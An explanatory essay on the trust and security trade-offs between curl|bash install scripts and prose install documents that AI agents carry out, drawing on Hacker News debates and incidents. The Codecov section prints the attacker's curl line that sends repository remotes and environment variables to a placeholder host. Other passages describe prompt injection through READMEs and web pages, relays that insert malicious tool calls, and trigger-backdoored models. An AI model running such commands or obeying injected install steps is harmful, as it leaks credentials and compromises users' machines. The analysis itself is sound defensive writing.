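# Install scripts versus AI agents that follow written install instructions: whom you trust and what you can check

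## How a script installs a program and how an agent does

An install script is a file of shell commands that puts a program on a computer. Makers of command-line tools have distributed software this way for many years, usually by giving users one line to copy from a web page into a terminal. Since the beginning of 2026, some have also published prose install documents, often in Markdown, that tell an AI agent what to install and how. The agent works out the commands itself. Either way, what happens on the user's machine depends on a file written by someone else, usually the software's maker, so the user has to decide whom to trust and what to check.

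### The script

A shell is the program behind a terminal window. It reads commands and runs them, and Bash and zsh are the common ones on Linux and macOS. A shell script is a text file of such commands in order, with tests and loops among them. Many projects offer theirs through a line of this form, which programmers call "curl | bash":

```
curl -fsSL ADDRESS | bash
```

ADDRESS stands for the web address of the script, which `curl` downloads. The option `f` makes `curl` fail on a server error instead of passing on the error page, `s` and `S` together hide the progress display but keep error messages, and `L` makes it follow redirects. The vertical bar, called a "pipe", sends the downloaded text straight into Bash, which runs the commands as they arrive. Unless the user downloads the file and reads it first, they don't see the script before it runs, and no copy stays on the disk.

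Bash runs the script with the user's permissions, so the script can read, change or delete any file the user can, including saved keys and passwords. It can also use the network. Changing system files requires administrator rights, which the user normally grants through the `sudo` command.

Bun, a program that runs JavaScript code, makes a convenient example because it consists of a single executable file. The script that Bun publishes first runs `uname`, which prints the operating system and processor type, and turns the result into the name of a download, such as `linux-x64`. A few tests refine that name. If the file `/etc/alpine-release` exists, the machine runs Alpine Linux, which is built on a different system library called musl, so the script takes the musl build. If a Mac is running the shell through Rosetta, Apple's translator for Intel programs on its newer ARM chips, the script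 takes the ARM build. If an Intel-type processor lacks AVX2, a set of fast arithmetic instructions, the script takes a "baseline" build. (According to Bun's *Installation* page, one build now covers both sorts of processor, and the old baseline name survives as an alias so that older scripts keep working.)

The script then creates the folder `~/.bun/bin`, downloads a zip file from Bun's releases on the code-hosting site GitHub, unpacks it, moves the program into place, marks it as executable and deletes the leftovers. It runs the program once to install "completions", which let the shell finish a half-typed command. If the shell cannot yet find a command named `bun`, the script adds two lines to the shell's configuration file to extend PATH, the list of folders where the shell looks for programs.

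The script doesn't check that the zip file is the one Bun's developers built. This is usually checked with a hash, a short fingerprint of a file that changes if any byte of the file changes. The publisher posts the hash, the user's machine computes it again from the download, and a mismatch shows that the file was damaged or swapped. Pinning means fixing an installation to one exact version, usually by its hash. The Bun script fetches the latest release by default, though a user can pass it a version label such as `bun-v1.3.3`. The label pins the version only loosely, because maintainers can later attach it to different contents, while a hash fits only one set of bytes. The installer for the agent instructions of Perfetto, a performance-analysis tool, is stricter because it translates a release number into the hash of one saved state of the project's files.

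### The agent's loop

An agent consists of a large language model and an agent program. The model takes in text and produces text, and it cannot read or change files by itself. The agent program is ordinary software that sends text to the model, runs the commands the model returns, and asks the user for permission where its settings require it. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex are agent programs. Developers often call the agent program the harness; Anthropic writes in its glossary, "Claude Code is the harness; Claude is the model inside it." A user can change either part and keep the other. Claude Code has a command for switching models mid-session, and Codex can send its requests to any server that supports OpenAI's interface.

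Bolin (2026), in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, sets out how Codex works through a task:

1. The agent program assembles a prompt, the text that the model will read. Besides the user's request it contains standing instructions, a list of the tools available (a shell among them), a description of the permissions in force, and the current folder and shell.
2. The model's reply is either a message to the user or a request for a tool call, for example to run a certain command.
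3. If it is a tool call, the agent program runs the command and appends the output to the prompt.
4. The agent program sends the longer prompt back to the model, and the cycle repeats until a reply comes back with a message to the user and no tool call.

One request can lead to hundreds of tool calls. The loop stops when the model outputs no more commands, which can happen before the work is finished. Anthropic advises users to supply a check the agent can run, such as a test, because otherwise the agent's judgment alone determines when the work is done.

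An agent starts with much the same power as a piped script. Claude Code can run any command the user could run from the terminal, according to Anthropic's *How Claude Code works*, but its permission modes limit what it does without approval. In manual mode, it asks the user before it edits a file or runs a shell command. In auto mode, now the usual starting mode, a separate classifier model reviews most actions and blocks those it rates as risky, without asking the user. A sandbox instead restricts which files, networks and credentials a program can reach, whatever the model outputs. Sandboxes can have gaps. The one in Codex covers its own shell tool, but Bolin notes that tools the user has connected from elsewhere run outside it.

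A user can paste or pipe an install document into the agent, so that it arrives as the user's own message, or give the agent an address, in which case the agent downloads the text and it arrives as the output of a tool. Either way, the model reads it in the same prompt as everything else, which makes prompt injection possible. Prompt injection is text placed in something an agent reads to make the agent do what the text's writer wants and the user does not want, such as a hidden line on a web page telling agents to upload the reader's password file. Researchers usually measure such attacks by the attack success rate, the share of trials in which the agent carries out the harmful action the attacker planted. Install documents are difficult for any defence because the user has told the agent to follow a stranger's instructions, and a harmful instruction can look much like the ones around it.

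### The same installation in English

Pete Koomen, a co-founder of the software company Optimizely, wrote English instructions as a substitute for Bun's install script and posted them on the programmers' forum Hacker News in January 2026. They are about 120 words long and contain no shell commands. They cover most of what the script does: detecting the system, picking the build, unpacking it to `~/.bun/bin`, updating the shell configuration, trying to install completions, and telling the user how to reload the shell.

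On a Linux laptop with an Intel processor and Bash, an agent might turn it into the following commands. The right-hand column shows what Koomen's wording leaves the agent to decide.

| Koomen's instruction | A command the agent might run | Choice left open |
|---|---|---|
| Detect the system and processor | `uname -sm` | Hardly any; several commands give the same answer |
| Baseline build if there is no AVX2; musl build on Alpine | `grep -c avx2 /proc/cpuinfo; ls /etc/alpine-release` | How to test; what to do on musl systems other than Alpine |
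| Download the appropriate zip from GitHub | `curl -fL -o /tmp/bun.zip ADDRESS` | Which release, and stable or test build; whether to check a hash |
| Extract it to `~/.bun/bin` | `mkdir -p ~/.bun/bin && unzip -j /tmp/bun.zip -d ~/.bun/bin` | What to do if `unzip` is missing; whether to overwrite an older copy; whether to keep the zip's inner folder |
| Make the program executable | `chmod +x ~/.bun/bin/bun` | None |
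| Clean up temporary files | `rm /tmp/bun.zip` | Which files count as temporary |
| Set BUN_INSTALL and PATH in the shell configuration | `printf '%s\n' 'export BUN_INSTALL=~/.bun' 'export PATH=$BUN_INSTALL/bin:$PATH' >> ~/.bashrc` | `.bashrc` or `.bash_profile`; what to do with Bun lines already there |
| Try to install completions | `~/.bun/bin/bun completions` | How long to keep trying after a failure |
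| Tell the user how to reload the configuration | None; the closing message gives `source ~/.bashrc` | Whether to test the new program first |

Most of these choices are harmless, but the inner folder can break the install. Bun's zip file holds the program inside a folder, and the script moves the program up one level. If an agent extracts the zip exactly as instructed and then adds `~/.bun/bin` to PATH, the shell won't find the program unless the agent checks the result and fixes it. (The `-j` option in the table avoids this by discarding folders.) If `unzip` is missing, Bun's script prints an error and exits. An agent could also stop, or it could unpack the file with another program or install `unzip` with administrator rights. Koomen's text gives no reason to prefer any of these.

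Koomen also refers to an Intel Mac running under Rosetta. Rosetta runs on ARM Macs, so he evidently means an ARM Mac that reports itself as Intel because the shell is running through the translator. A competent model will probably interpret it that way. In the Hacker News copy, the agent also has to recognize the configuration file of fish, another shell, even though its name has become a web link, presumably through automatic formatting.

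The script's author settled all these questions beforehand, some of them badly. The script treats any system it does not recognise as `linux-x64`. Its only test for musl is the Alpine file, although Bun lists Void Linux beside Alpine as a system that needs the musl build. On Void Linux, the script would fetch the wrong file and still report success, because it prints its success message before it first runs the program and ignores any failure after that. An agent that tried the program and saw the error could go back for the right build. Neither the script nor Koomen's text includes a hash check, and neither pins a version unless the user adds one.

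### From Koomen's idea to install.md and skill.md

Koomen proposed the idea on the social network X early in January 2026, and within days Jed White of the search company Andi had built a tool that could run it, called claude-run. The site frontpage reproduces White's announcement. A Markdown file whose first line names claude-run can be run like a shell script; the tool removes that line and passes the rest to Claude Code. White credited Koomen and used the Bun installation as an example, piping an `install.md` file into claude-run instead of a script into Bash.

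In *claude-switcher*, a walk-through of the tool, tumf (2026) explains that such a file cannot run code by default, so an installation needs an extra flag, `bypassPermissions`, which lets the model's commands run without approval. White, posting as jedwhite, later added support for files piped in from the web and noted that claude-run applies flags on a file's first line. A downloaded document can therefore include the flag that lets commands run without approval.

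Mintlify, a company that hosts documentation for other software makers, tried to turn the idea into a standard. Its first draft, Mintlify's *The /install.md file* (2026), carries the date 10 January and stays close to Koomen. Only a heading with the software's name was compulsory, and authors were to describe what should happen and leave the commands to the agent. The version that the company announced on 16 January was tighter. Ryaboy (2026), in *install.md*, gives these parts:

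- a heading with the product's name, and a short description
- a request in the first person, to install the product and carry out every step autonomously
- OBJECTIVE, the state the installation should reach
- DONE WHEN, a condition that the agent can test
- TODO, a checklist of steps
- the steps in detail, with commands in code blocks
- EXECUTE NOW, a closing order that repeats the goal

The DONE WHEN line supplies the check that the bare loop lacks. In Ryaboy's example, which installs Mintlify's own command-line tool, the work is done when a documentation server on the user's machine answers at port 3000. The checklist begins with the version of Node.js, the JavaScript system the tool depends on, and ends with that test. Most of the text in between is literal commands such as `npm i -g mint`. The example is much closer to an annotated script than Koomen's text was, although Ryaboy describes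 the format as giving outcomes rather than exact commands. It still leaves gaps. For instance, it requires Node.js 20.17.0 or newer but gives no instructions for a user who has an older version.

Mintlify explained in its documentation at the time that the first-person opening frames the file as a user's request in order to trigger autonomous execution, so the document's author is writing in the user's name. Often no person wrote the file, because Mintlify generated one automatically for each public site it hosted unless the customer supplied one. Its software selected pages with words such as "install", "quickstart" or "overview" in their titles or paths, condensed them into commands and a checklist, and dropped the troubleshooting sections.

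Mintlify dropped the standard after five days. Hacker News readers had argued over whether it made installing software any safer, but Ryaboy, explaining the decision on 21 January, cited little adoption and greater "momentum behind skills". A skill is a folder or file of written instructions that an agent loads to do a particular kind of task. Anthropic introduced the format and made it an open standard in 2025, as the programmer Simon Willison recorded on his weblog. Mintlify's replacement, `skill.md`, combines instructions for installing a product with instructions for using it, and one command adds it to the user's agent. Claude Code shows the model a short description of each skill at the start of a session and loads the full text when a task needs it. Unlike an `install.md` file, which was used once, a skill stays on the machine and can steer later sessions.

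### What projects publish now

Projects kept publishing install instructions for agents after the install.md standard ended. The *Installation* guide for oh-my-opencode, an add-on to the agent program OpenCode, opens with a line for users to paste into their agent. The line directs the agent to the guide's own address for instructions. The guide marks running the installer by hand as "not recommended". Cargo, a platform for sales data, writes its instructions directly to the agent. They tell it to check whether the tool is already installed, install it through the package manager npm if it isn't, skip any step that is already done, and follow the branch for Claude Code, Codex or Cursor. Brethof AI's *Install brethof-brain*, a page for a product that stores agents' memories, reduces the user's part to typing one sentence to the agent. The access key goes into a separate window that the agent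 can't see.

Many tools still offer a one-line install script. The website of llama.cpp, a widely used program for running language models on one's own computer, shows a curl command near the top of its front page, and Bun still offers its script alongside package managers. A script can also install an agent program. The setup guide of anywhere-agents, a project that configures coding agents, recommends installing Claude Code with a curl command rather than npm, because the copy installed by curl updates itself in the background.

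## The arguments for scripts, for prose and for combining them

Most of the public argument over these two methods took place in two Hacker News threads in January 2026, one under White's announcement of claude-run and the other under Mintlify's proposal. The site frontpage has copies of both, with user names. Hardly anyone offered measurements. People argued from what they knew of deployment tools and coding agents, and some continued a much older argument about whether it is ever sensible to pipe a script from the web into a shell.

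### For scripts

People who prefer scripts mostly start by arguing that scripts are repeatable. A Bash script is deterministic, meaning it does the same thing whenever it runs under the same conditions. A user can therefore send it to 20 AI systems or someone fluent in Bash for review, as inlined told Mintlify's staff, and the findings will still hold when the script runs. An agent picks its commands anew each time. inlined compared this to letting Excel's Copilot feature fill in a cell instead of asking the AI for a formula and keeping it. constantcrying wrote that most of the big trends in software deployment have aimed at predictability, and that a script at least does the same thing on every machine in the same state.

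Many people can also share the reading. Martin Tournoij, a programmer who has defended piped install scripts on his website, points out that the scripts for Docker, Rust, Yarn and the shell add-on oh-my-zsh sit in those projects' source code and get the same scrutiny as the software itself. (Tournoij admits that nothing guarantees the server sends out the same file.)

catlifeonmars said that a reviewer of prose has to audit both the written instructions and how the agent interprets them, which depends on the model, the context and the temperature (the setting that controls how much chance enters the model's output). Existing analysis programs can examine a shell script without running it. chme thought the problem was natural language itself, because someone who misunderstands a sentence has to ask whoever wrote it, while someone who misunderstands code can run it and test their guess. White's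 own example had the agent download "the right binary". wiether replied that this was far too vague, that they would send back a product manager's request worded like that, and that they couldn't see how such instructions were easier to audit than a script with the addresses and paths written out.

DocTomoe, replying to jedwhite, described a failure that testing would miss. Someone writes a prompt that ends with an instruction to clean up, the model handles it sensibly 26 times, and on the 27th run it deletes everything on the disk. By then people trust the prompt. DocTomoe's example concerned log files, but Koomen's Bun instructions also tell the agent to clean up temporary files. A string of successful runs is weak evidence that a prompt has no rare fault. If a prompt does damage in one run out of a hundred, and the runs are independent, there is about a 77 percent chance that 26 runs will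 do no damage.

akdev1l doubted that the prose would stay short, either. In their experience, prompts grow to hundreds of lines as people patch one edge case after another, and nobody can change one part without risking side effects elsewhere. The result, they wrote, is "like code but strictly worse".

An install document also needs a model to carry it out, whereas a script can run on a machine that has no agent. For this reason, roywiggins called the model "a massive dependency" and asked why anyone should spend paid tokens on an installation. rarisma estimated that Claude takes 10 to 20 seconds to check which version of Node.js a machine has, or longer if a person must approve the command, compared with milliseconds for a script. chme asked how automated build servers, which often install software on every build, would work if each installation needed a model.

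Maintainers would also have to support users whose installations went wrong. Szpadel imagined a ticket from a user who tried to install the program with MiniMax M2, a model Szpadel considered unreliable. The installation failed, and now the user's documents folder is missing. The maintainer can't reproduce the fault, and nobody knows who is responsible for it. chme suggested drily that this might be the appeal of the format, since it moves responsibility for errors from the person who wrote the instructions to the person who ran them.

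Mintlify conceded part of this case. In its first draft of the standard, it granted that shell scripts "execute identically regardless of who runs them" and recommended using a package manager when one carries the software. During the thread, a Mintlify employee who posts as skeptrune promised to list agents' unpredictability among the format's downsides.

### For prose

Koomen argues that people find large amounts of code hard to read, and that a prompt can make the author's purpose clear where code can't. Bun's install script runs to hundreds of lines. A user can ask a coding agent to audit it, but then, as Koomen wrote in the thread on frontpage, the user has to trust that the authors haven't hidden instructions to the model in it. Koomen's English version is short enough to read at a glance, and it lets the user "audit the intentions of the programmer". Koomen did not claim that models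 are inherently trustworthy.

In reply, catlifeonmars said they usually read the source code first because it shows precisely how something will behave. smaudet objected to counting lines because anyone can shorten a script by hiding commands inside other commands, and because an agent involves a model with billions of parameters.

White came to a similar view after using claude-run, writing in the opening post of the frontpage thread that Markdown files had unexpectedly turned out "more auditable" than shell scripts. chrismorgan found it bizarre to hear this about tools that occasionally delete people's entire drives. White granted that unpredictable output makes auditing harder, but argued that ease of understanding is also part of auditing, and that developers weigh the two differently. White also thought a Claude Code user who sets permissions carefully is no more likely to lose a drive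 than a competent command-line user. In years of technical support, White had helped many people who had wrecked a Windows installation or deleted files they needed without using AI.

Mintlify set out its defence in the security part of an FAQ. The question it chose to answer was whether install.md was just "curl | bash" with extra steps, which Ryaboy called a fair concern before giving three replies:

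- Users can read the instructions before anything runs, and the intent is clear, "unlike obfuscated scripts".
- Users can configure an agent to ask for approval before each command, so they see every action and can reject it.
- The file describes outcomes in natural language, and "malicious intent is harder to hide than in a shell script".

The FAQ then says that people should still use install.md files only from sources they trust, as with any other installation method.

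rarisma quoted the FAQ back at Mintlify and answered it. Ordinary install scripts aren't obfuscated, and anyone can read them. An author who wanted to obfuscate one would not publish an install.md file instead. Approving each step gives back the time that the agent was supposed to save. Security writers had their own reasons to doubt that readable text is safe text: Meller (2026), in *From magic to malware*, treats the Markdown skills of the agent program OpenClaw as an attack surface.

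In the thread's most quoted remark, skeptrune preferred Markdown to Bash "because at least Claude kind of has your best interests at heart". heliumtera called it a wild thing to say, unless the whole proposal was satire. skeptrune explained that Bash runs whatever arrives, while a user who gives the same job to an agent can also ask whether it sees anything nefarious in the file, or tell it to check with them before each install. themikesanto replied that a user can ask an agent the same questions about any install script. skeptrune agreed, but suggested that asking about a Markdown file feels more natural. vimda thought the approach only changed the attack vector, because models have repeatedly failed when working with unvetted documents.

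JoshPurtell made a statistical version of skeptrune's argument, predicting that at some point, if not already, Claude will install malware less often on average than people do, just as Waymo's driverless cars crash less often than human drivers. By this reasoning, the agent can sometimes install malware and still be the safer choice, as long as it does so less often than the people who would otherwise paste the command, usually without reading anything.

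The other argument for prose is that an agent can look at the machine it is installing on, while a script's author has to foresee every machine the script will meet. Ryaboy contrasted a script that may not "figure out" a user's Arch Linux setup with an agent that looks at the setup before choosing between npm and pnpm, or between a new project and an existing one. luqs1 added that a truly comprehensive install script is thankless to write, and that a shell script rules out Windows. In a post about a talk at the investment firm Sequoia, the AI researcher Andrej Karpathy (2026) listed installation by prose among the new things that language models make possible. He asked why anyone should write a complex Bash script when they can put the installation into words and say "just show this to your LLM". In his account, the model is an advanced interpreter of English that fits the installation to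 the user's setup and debugs problems as they come up.

Sébastien, in *Markdown-based Installation (MD Scripts)*, develops Karpathy's idea further. Prose explains the intent behind an installation instead of fixing a single path through it, so when a step fails the agent can read the error, diagnose it and propose a fix without anyone contacting the maintainer. One Markdown file can replace a Bash script, a PowerShell script for Windows and separate files for Docker and Homebrew. Because the agent carries out the documentation itself, the documentation and the installer can't become inconsistent. Sébastien expects the agent to ask before destructive steps, and lists four drawbacks: two runs may take different paths, the user must trust the model's interpretation of security-sensitive steps, every installation uses tokens, and the method needs a capable model that can operate a shell.

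themikesanto had argued that existing scripts would give an agent better guidance than a new kind of file. skeptrune reported the opposite. Mintlify had tried feeding install scripts to agents, and it worked, "but a lot worse than this install.md thing".

Koomen said the argument also applies beyond install scripts, which are simply an example that current models can handle correctly from a reasonably descriptive prompt. In time, Koomen suggested, people may exchange more and more software as prompts instead of compiled code. Koomen called the agent's role in this a "runtime for prose", a runtime being the software that executes a program.

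### For combining them

Several commenters liked what an agent can do but did not want it to replace the script. roywiggins proposed keeping the regular installer and adding a file of information that a model can use if the installer fails. roywiggins argued that if the script would work, the user should run it, because an agent might fail for no good reason. If the script fails, either a person or a model can follow the file as a troubleshooting guide. If that fails too, the user is hopefully no worse off, since the script had already failed. roywiggins made an exception for people who let the agent run without approvals, for whom "the consequences are on them". ollien suggested something similar, a skill containing the install script and troubleshooting notes. skeptrune mostly agreed that an agent should help after a failure and not jump straight to installing.

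nobodywillobsrv wanted to use the model earlier. The user gives the agent an install.md file and asks it to write an install script, and can then read either text before running anything. catlifeonmars liked this better than Mintlify's version because the script is reproducible and running it again costs no tokens. In White's thread linkregister made the same suggestion, guessing that Claude Code was reliable to "one and a half nines", somewhere between 90 and 99 percent. White, as jedwhite, answered that this was already how they handled many quick automation jobs.

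Others suggested using the prose to produce an ordinary script. chme said that if a model can write the script from the prose, the developer can have it do so once, validate the result and publish that. michaelmior objected that users would again need to check a script someone else has approved. chme answered that they can ask a model whether the script does anything bad, which should work at least as well as asking a model to write one. franga2000 said that having the publisher store the generated script on a server and audit it before release amounts to "caching and deduplicating the auditing work". vrighter asked why a model should still be involved when projects already provide scripts that anyone can audit.

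catlifeonmars had a proposal that leaves the model out of the installation and uses it as a reviewer. The model audits the shell script, and the user then records its hash, so that a later copy with the same hash needs no second audit. akomtu suggested that authors comment every difficult line of a script in English and have a model check that the comments match the code. verdverm would have the model write the inputs for established configuration tools such as Ansible, Puppet and Chef, once, and let those tools do the installing. 0o_MrPatrick_o0, who also favoured such tools, asked what happens when an agent crashes halfway through an installation. Configuration tools aim to be idempotent, which means that running them a second time leaves the machine in the same state as running them once, so a user can recover from an interruption by starting again.

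White combined the two differently, putting the parts that must not vary into ordinary scripts and having a Markdown file call them. White said this arrangement had produced "remarkably consistent" results in real test suites. shakna disagreed that it solved the problem, arguing that a chain with one unpredictable step is unpredictable as a whole. White replied that the fixed steps can still compute the figures while the model only summarises them. An installer, however, has to change the machine and can't limit the model to writing a report.

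Mintlify itself moved partly in this direction. skeptrune said the company was at least thinking about generating install scripts instead of Markdown. When Ryaboy introduced the replacement format, `skill.md`, he advised authors to make choices for the agent wherever they could do so confidently, because the agent then makes fewer errors.

### "You have to trust the author anyway"

Another group thinks the choice of format hardly matters for security, an argument older than coding agents. Kenton Varda (2015), in *Is curl|bash insecure?*, defended the install command for Sandstorm, a security product that runs each web application in its own sandbox. Critics had complained that piping a script into Bash gives a website full access to the machine. Varda replied that traditional Unix software always runs with the full authority of the user who starts it, and that most package managers run scripts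 from the package with administrator rights at install time. The piped command only makes it visible that "anything you install can pwn you" (take over your machine). Anyone who wants to install software without giving it that power needs a separate computer, a virtual machine or perhaps a separate user account.

Varda took a different complaint more seriously, that a third party might swap the download for a malicious one. Sandstorm already served everything over HTTPS, which encrypts the connection and confirms the server's identity. On the day of the post, it added a way to check the installer against the developers' PGP signatures, which outsiders can't forge without a developer's private key. The check adds nothing to HTTPS unless the user confirms the matching public key through a channel other than the developer's own server. So even by Varda's argument, a user who trusts the author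 still has to establish that the file came from the author.

Tournoij argues that nobody is going to audit all of oh-my-zsh, so a person who trusts it enough to run it has no reason to distrust its install script. The alternatives that people call safer are no easier to inspect, since building a program from source often means running tens of thousands of lines of generated configuration code that nobody reads. But a user may trust that a vendor's script isn't malicious and still not know where it will put files, whether they can undo its changes, or what it will do if a tool is missing. Tournoij regards these as serious concerns, though not security concerns.

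rarisma brought the argument into the install.md thread. Anyone with doubts about an author's honesty shouldn't run the software, and putting Claude around the installation won't help much, because the malware is probably in the program and not in the installer.

Koomen anticipated the objection that people shouldn't install software from those they don't trust. "That is, of course, true," Koomen wrote, but argued that it misses the point. An agent can carry out instructions that the user has understood, and Koomen holds that this transparency more than makes up for what the user loses in determinism and efficiency. Tournoij's second sense of trust supports this argument, because an honest author may still change a shell configuration in ways the user would have refused, and a short English text gives the user a chance to notice.

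The same argument is harder to use in defence of prose. Varda and Tournoij were writing about scripts, where the author's text determines what runs, but even an honest author can't vouch for what an agent will do with written instructions. Koomen acknowledged this further down the thread, describing a trade-off between "do I trust the programmer?" and "do I trust the LLM?", and expected people to become more comfortable with the second as models get better at following instructions. catlifeonmars suggested that the choice hardly matters because both options are dangerous.

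### The questions in dispute

Five factual questions divide these positions:

1. **Who is trusted?** Prose brings in the model, its maker and the agent program. They may be additional parties to trust, or they may replace some of the trust that users now place in the author.
2. **Which text is easier to check?** Koomen and White mean that a reader can see what the author wants. Their critics mean that a reader can work out what the machine will do.
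3. **Does the agent protect the user?** skeptrune's remark about Claude depends on the agent noticing a harmful instruction in a document that the user has told it to follow.
4. **Do results repeat?** DocTomoe's 27th run matters only if agents given the same document do in fact take different paths, and if some of those paths do damage.
5. **What does a new model change?** PunchyHamster warned that a different agent may follow the same instructions differently. White's answer was to request a model by its dated version, but zephen doubted that providers never slip in silent fixes.

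## Who has to be trusted in each case

In computer security, a trusted party is anyone whose mistake or bad faith could harm the user, even if the user has never heard of them. A person who installs software therefore trusts many parties besides its author, and most of them are the same whether a script or an agent does the installing.

### The parties behind a script

When a user copies a one-line command from a web page and runs it, any of these parties could do harm, roughly in the order in which they come into play:

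1. The author, who can write a malicious script or make an honest mistake.
2. Whoever controls the page that shows the command. These pages often load advertising and analytics code from other companies, and dstreefkerk, in *The curl*, points out that any of that code could rewrite the command. It could also leave the visible text alone and change only what the user's clipboard receives.
3. The host that stores and serves the script, along with anyone who steals the host's credentials.
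4. The connection. This includes the system that turns a domain name into a server's address, the authorities that issue certificates for HTTPS, and any redirect on the way. A faulty redirect on the vendor's own site can send `curl` elsewhere while the command still shows the vendor's name.
5. Whoever supplies the files that the script downloads, such as Bun's zip file on GitHub.
6. The makers of the shell and of the ordinary programs the script calls, such as `curl` and `unzip`.

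A script written in good faith can also do harm if the download stops partway, because Bash runs commands as they arrive. If the connection drops in the middle of `rm -rf ~/.tool/tmp`, which deletes a temporary folder, Bash may receive only `rm -rf ~/`, which deletes the user's home folder. dstreefkerk advises authors to put all the commands in functions and call the main function on the last line, so that an incomplete download runs nothing.

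### An altered script: Codecov, 2021

Codecov provides a service that measures how much of a program its tests cover. It used to distribute a shell script, the Bash Uploader, that sent test reports to Codecov. The script installed nothing, but customers downloaded and ran it much as they would an install script, usually on automated build servers.

According to Codecov's *Post-Mortem / Root Cause Analysis (April 2021)* (2021), an attacker found a storage key in a hidden layer of a Docker image, a packaged copy of Codecov's software that anyone could download. The key gave write access to the Google storage from which Codecov served the script. The attacker added one line, shown here with ADDRESS in place of the attacker's server:

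```
curl -sm 0.5 -d "$(git remote -v)<<<<<< ENV $(env)" ADDRESS || true
```

This line sends the attacker the address of the customer's code repository and all the environment variables, the named values that programs in a session share. On a build server, these often include passwords and access keys. The line displays nothing, times out after half a second, and lets the rest of the script continue if the upload fails, so a customer would see a normal run.

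The altered script was live during 108 periods between 31 January and 1 April 2021, according to Codecov's *Bash Uploader Security Update* (2021). Codecov's add-ons for three build services fetched the same script, so users of those add-ons also ran the extra line. The security company Rapid7 later disclosed that the attackers had accessed some of its source code, according to Security Magazine's *Rapid7 victim of a software supply chain breach*.

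The attack ended because one customer found that the downloaded script's hash didn't match the one on GitHub. The attacker had changed only the copy on the server. Tournoij argues that many people read the scripts in a project's source code, but they would not have seen this change there. Even someone who read the server's copy would have found nothing wrong if they did so between two of the 108 periods when it was altered.

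### The shell, the compiler and the model

The shell comes last in the list, and few users think about it at all. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, made the classic argument that they have to trust such programs anyway. Thompson (1984), in *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, describes a trick with a compiler, the program that translates source code into the machine code a computer runs. It takes three steps:

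1. Thompson changes the C compiler so that whenever it compiles Unix's login program, it adds a second password that Thompson knows. The source code of the login program stays clean, but anyone who reads the compiler's source will see the change.
2. Thompson makes a second change, so that whenever the compiler compiles its own source code, it inserts both changes into the new compiler.
3. Thompson compiles this version once, installs it, and deletes both changes from the source. From then on, the installed compiler puts them back every time someone builds a new compiler from the clean source.

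A person could now read every line of both programs and find no trace of the extra password. Thompson concluded, "You can't trust code that you did not totally create yourself." His argument covers any program that handles other programs, and he mentions assemblers, loaders and processor microcode. It also applies to a shell, and to an agent that turns an install document into commands. A user who reads the script or document carefully still has to trust the shell or agent that carries it out.

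The shell is much easier to trust than a model, though, because its rules are published and fixed. The Open Group's standard (2024) defines the shell's command language, including how a shell splits a line into words, replaces variables with their values and runs the result. ISO (2026) issued the current edition as an international standard. Bash adds features, which its manual describes, and an installed copy behaves the same way until someone updates it. If a shell breaks these rules, anyone can demonstrate the fault in a few lines and report it as a bug. Nobody can look up which commands a model will produce when it reads "clean up temporary files". Its developer can publish guidelines for its behaviour, but they don't determine its output, which comes from billions of numbers set in training.

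Published rules make some checks possible, but they don't defeat Thompson's trick, since a user's copy of the shell might secretly break them. In a later PhD dissertation, David A. Wheeler describes a countermeasure. He compiles the compiler's source with a second, independent compiler, uses the result to compile the same source again, and compares the output with the suspect compiler byte by byte. This works because a compiler should always turn the same source into the same bytes. A user can't check Claude this way because they have no second, independent copy that ought to give identical answers.

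### What an agent adds

When an agent follows a prose install document, the fixed script disappears but the parties behind it mostly stay. Someone still writes the document, hosts it and supplies the downloads, and the agent's commands still go through a shell. The agent adds four more kinds of party:

1. The model's developer, and anyone else who handles the model before it reaches the user. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026) warns that modified models on public download sites can contain malicious behaviour that appears only when a certain trigger turns up in the text.
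2. The maker of the agent program, the makers of the software packages inside it, and whoever delivers its updates.
3. Any service that relays requests between the agent program and the model.
4. The writer of every web page, file and error message that the agent reads along the way.

People who use an agent to avoid piping scripts into Bash may have installed the agent that way. Anthropic's *Advanced setup* recommends this method for Claude Code on macOS and Linux. Users who follow it have to trust Anthropic's script once, and Anthropic's update system for as long as background updates stay on.

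Relays are services that offer many companies' models through one address, often at lower prices. People who connect directly to Anthropic or OpenAI don't need one. A relay decrypts each request before forwarding it, so it can read the user's text, substitute a cheaper model or change the reply. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (2026) explains that if a relay changes a tool call, the agent program runs the changed version with the developer's permissions.

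Liu and colleagues examined 428 relays and found nine that inserted malicious tool calls and 18 that misused credentials passing through them, according to *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* (2026). An honest operator's relay software can also be compromised. In March 2026, attackers released two versions of LiteLLM, a widely used relay program, that stole credentials and cryptocurrency wallets.

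Wu, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *What the Middleman Delivers*, tested 20 relays that offered GPT-6 Astra or Claude Opus 5 and confirmed no malicious insertion in 3,332 replies to requests about code and setup. This offers limited reassurance. If about 2 percent of relays are malicious, as in the larger survey, a random sample of 20 would contain none about 65 percent of the time. Wu and colleagues did not choose their relays at random, and they sent single requests without letting an agent run anything, so they could have missed attacks that wait for a real working session. Four relays returned tool calls even though the request had disabled them, but none did so when the researchers repeated the tests 11 to 18 days later.

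The largest group the user has to trust is everyone whose text the agent reads, and nobody can list these people in advance. If a program run by an install script prints an error message, the script's later commands stay as the author wrote them. With an agent, the message goes into the prompt and can affect the next command. *Practical Agentic Software Supply Chain Security* (Monperrus, 2026) gives the example of a package whose README file recommends running one more command "for best performance". The command pipes the attacker's script into Bash, and an agent that reads the file while setting up a project may run it. The user would then face all the risks of an install script without having chosen the script.

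How many new risks a user takes on depends on whether they already use an agent. Someone who works with Claude Code all day has already accepted the risk from Anthropic and its updates. For them, an install document adds the risks from its author, the pages it leads to and the model misreading it. Someone who sets up an agent only to install a program takes on all of these risks at once. Both users still have to trust the author, because a dishonest author can do harm whenever the agent fails to notice.

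### A compromised agent program: Cursor's marketplace, 2026

On 29 October 2026, an attacker replaced the Claude Code extension in the marketplace of Cursor, an AI code editor. According to Cursor's *Security notice*, the altered copy was available from about 2:27 am to 1:35 pm Pacific time.

The extension collected details such as the user's name, Git email address and public internet address, and sent the attacker a report on the machine. It also tried to let the attacker log in by SSH, a system for controlling a computer remotely. This failed on most machines because the extension had no administrator rights, but it still saved the attacker's key and installed background programs that kept trying to connect. Uninstalling the extension didn't necessarily remove them, so Cursor published scripts for affected users to download and run.

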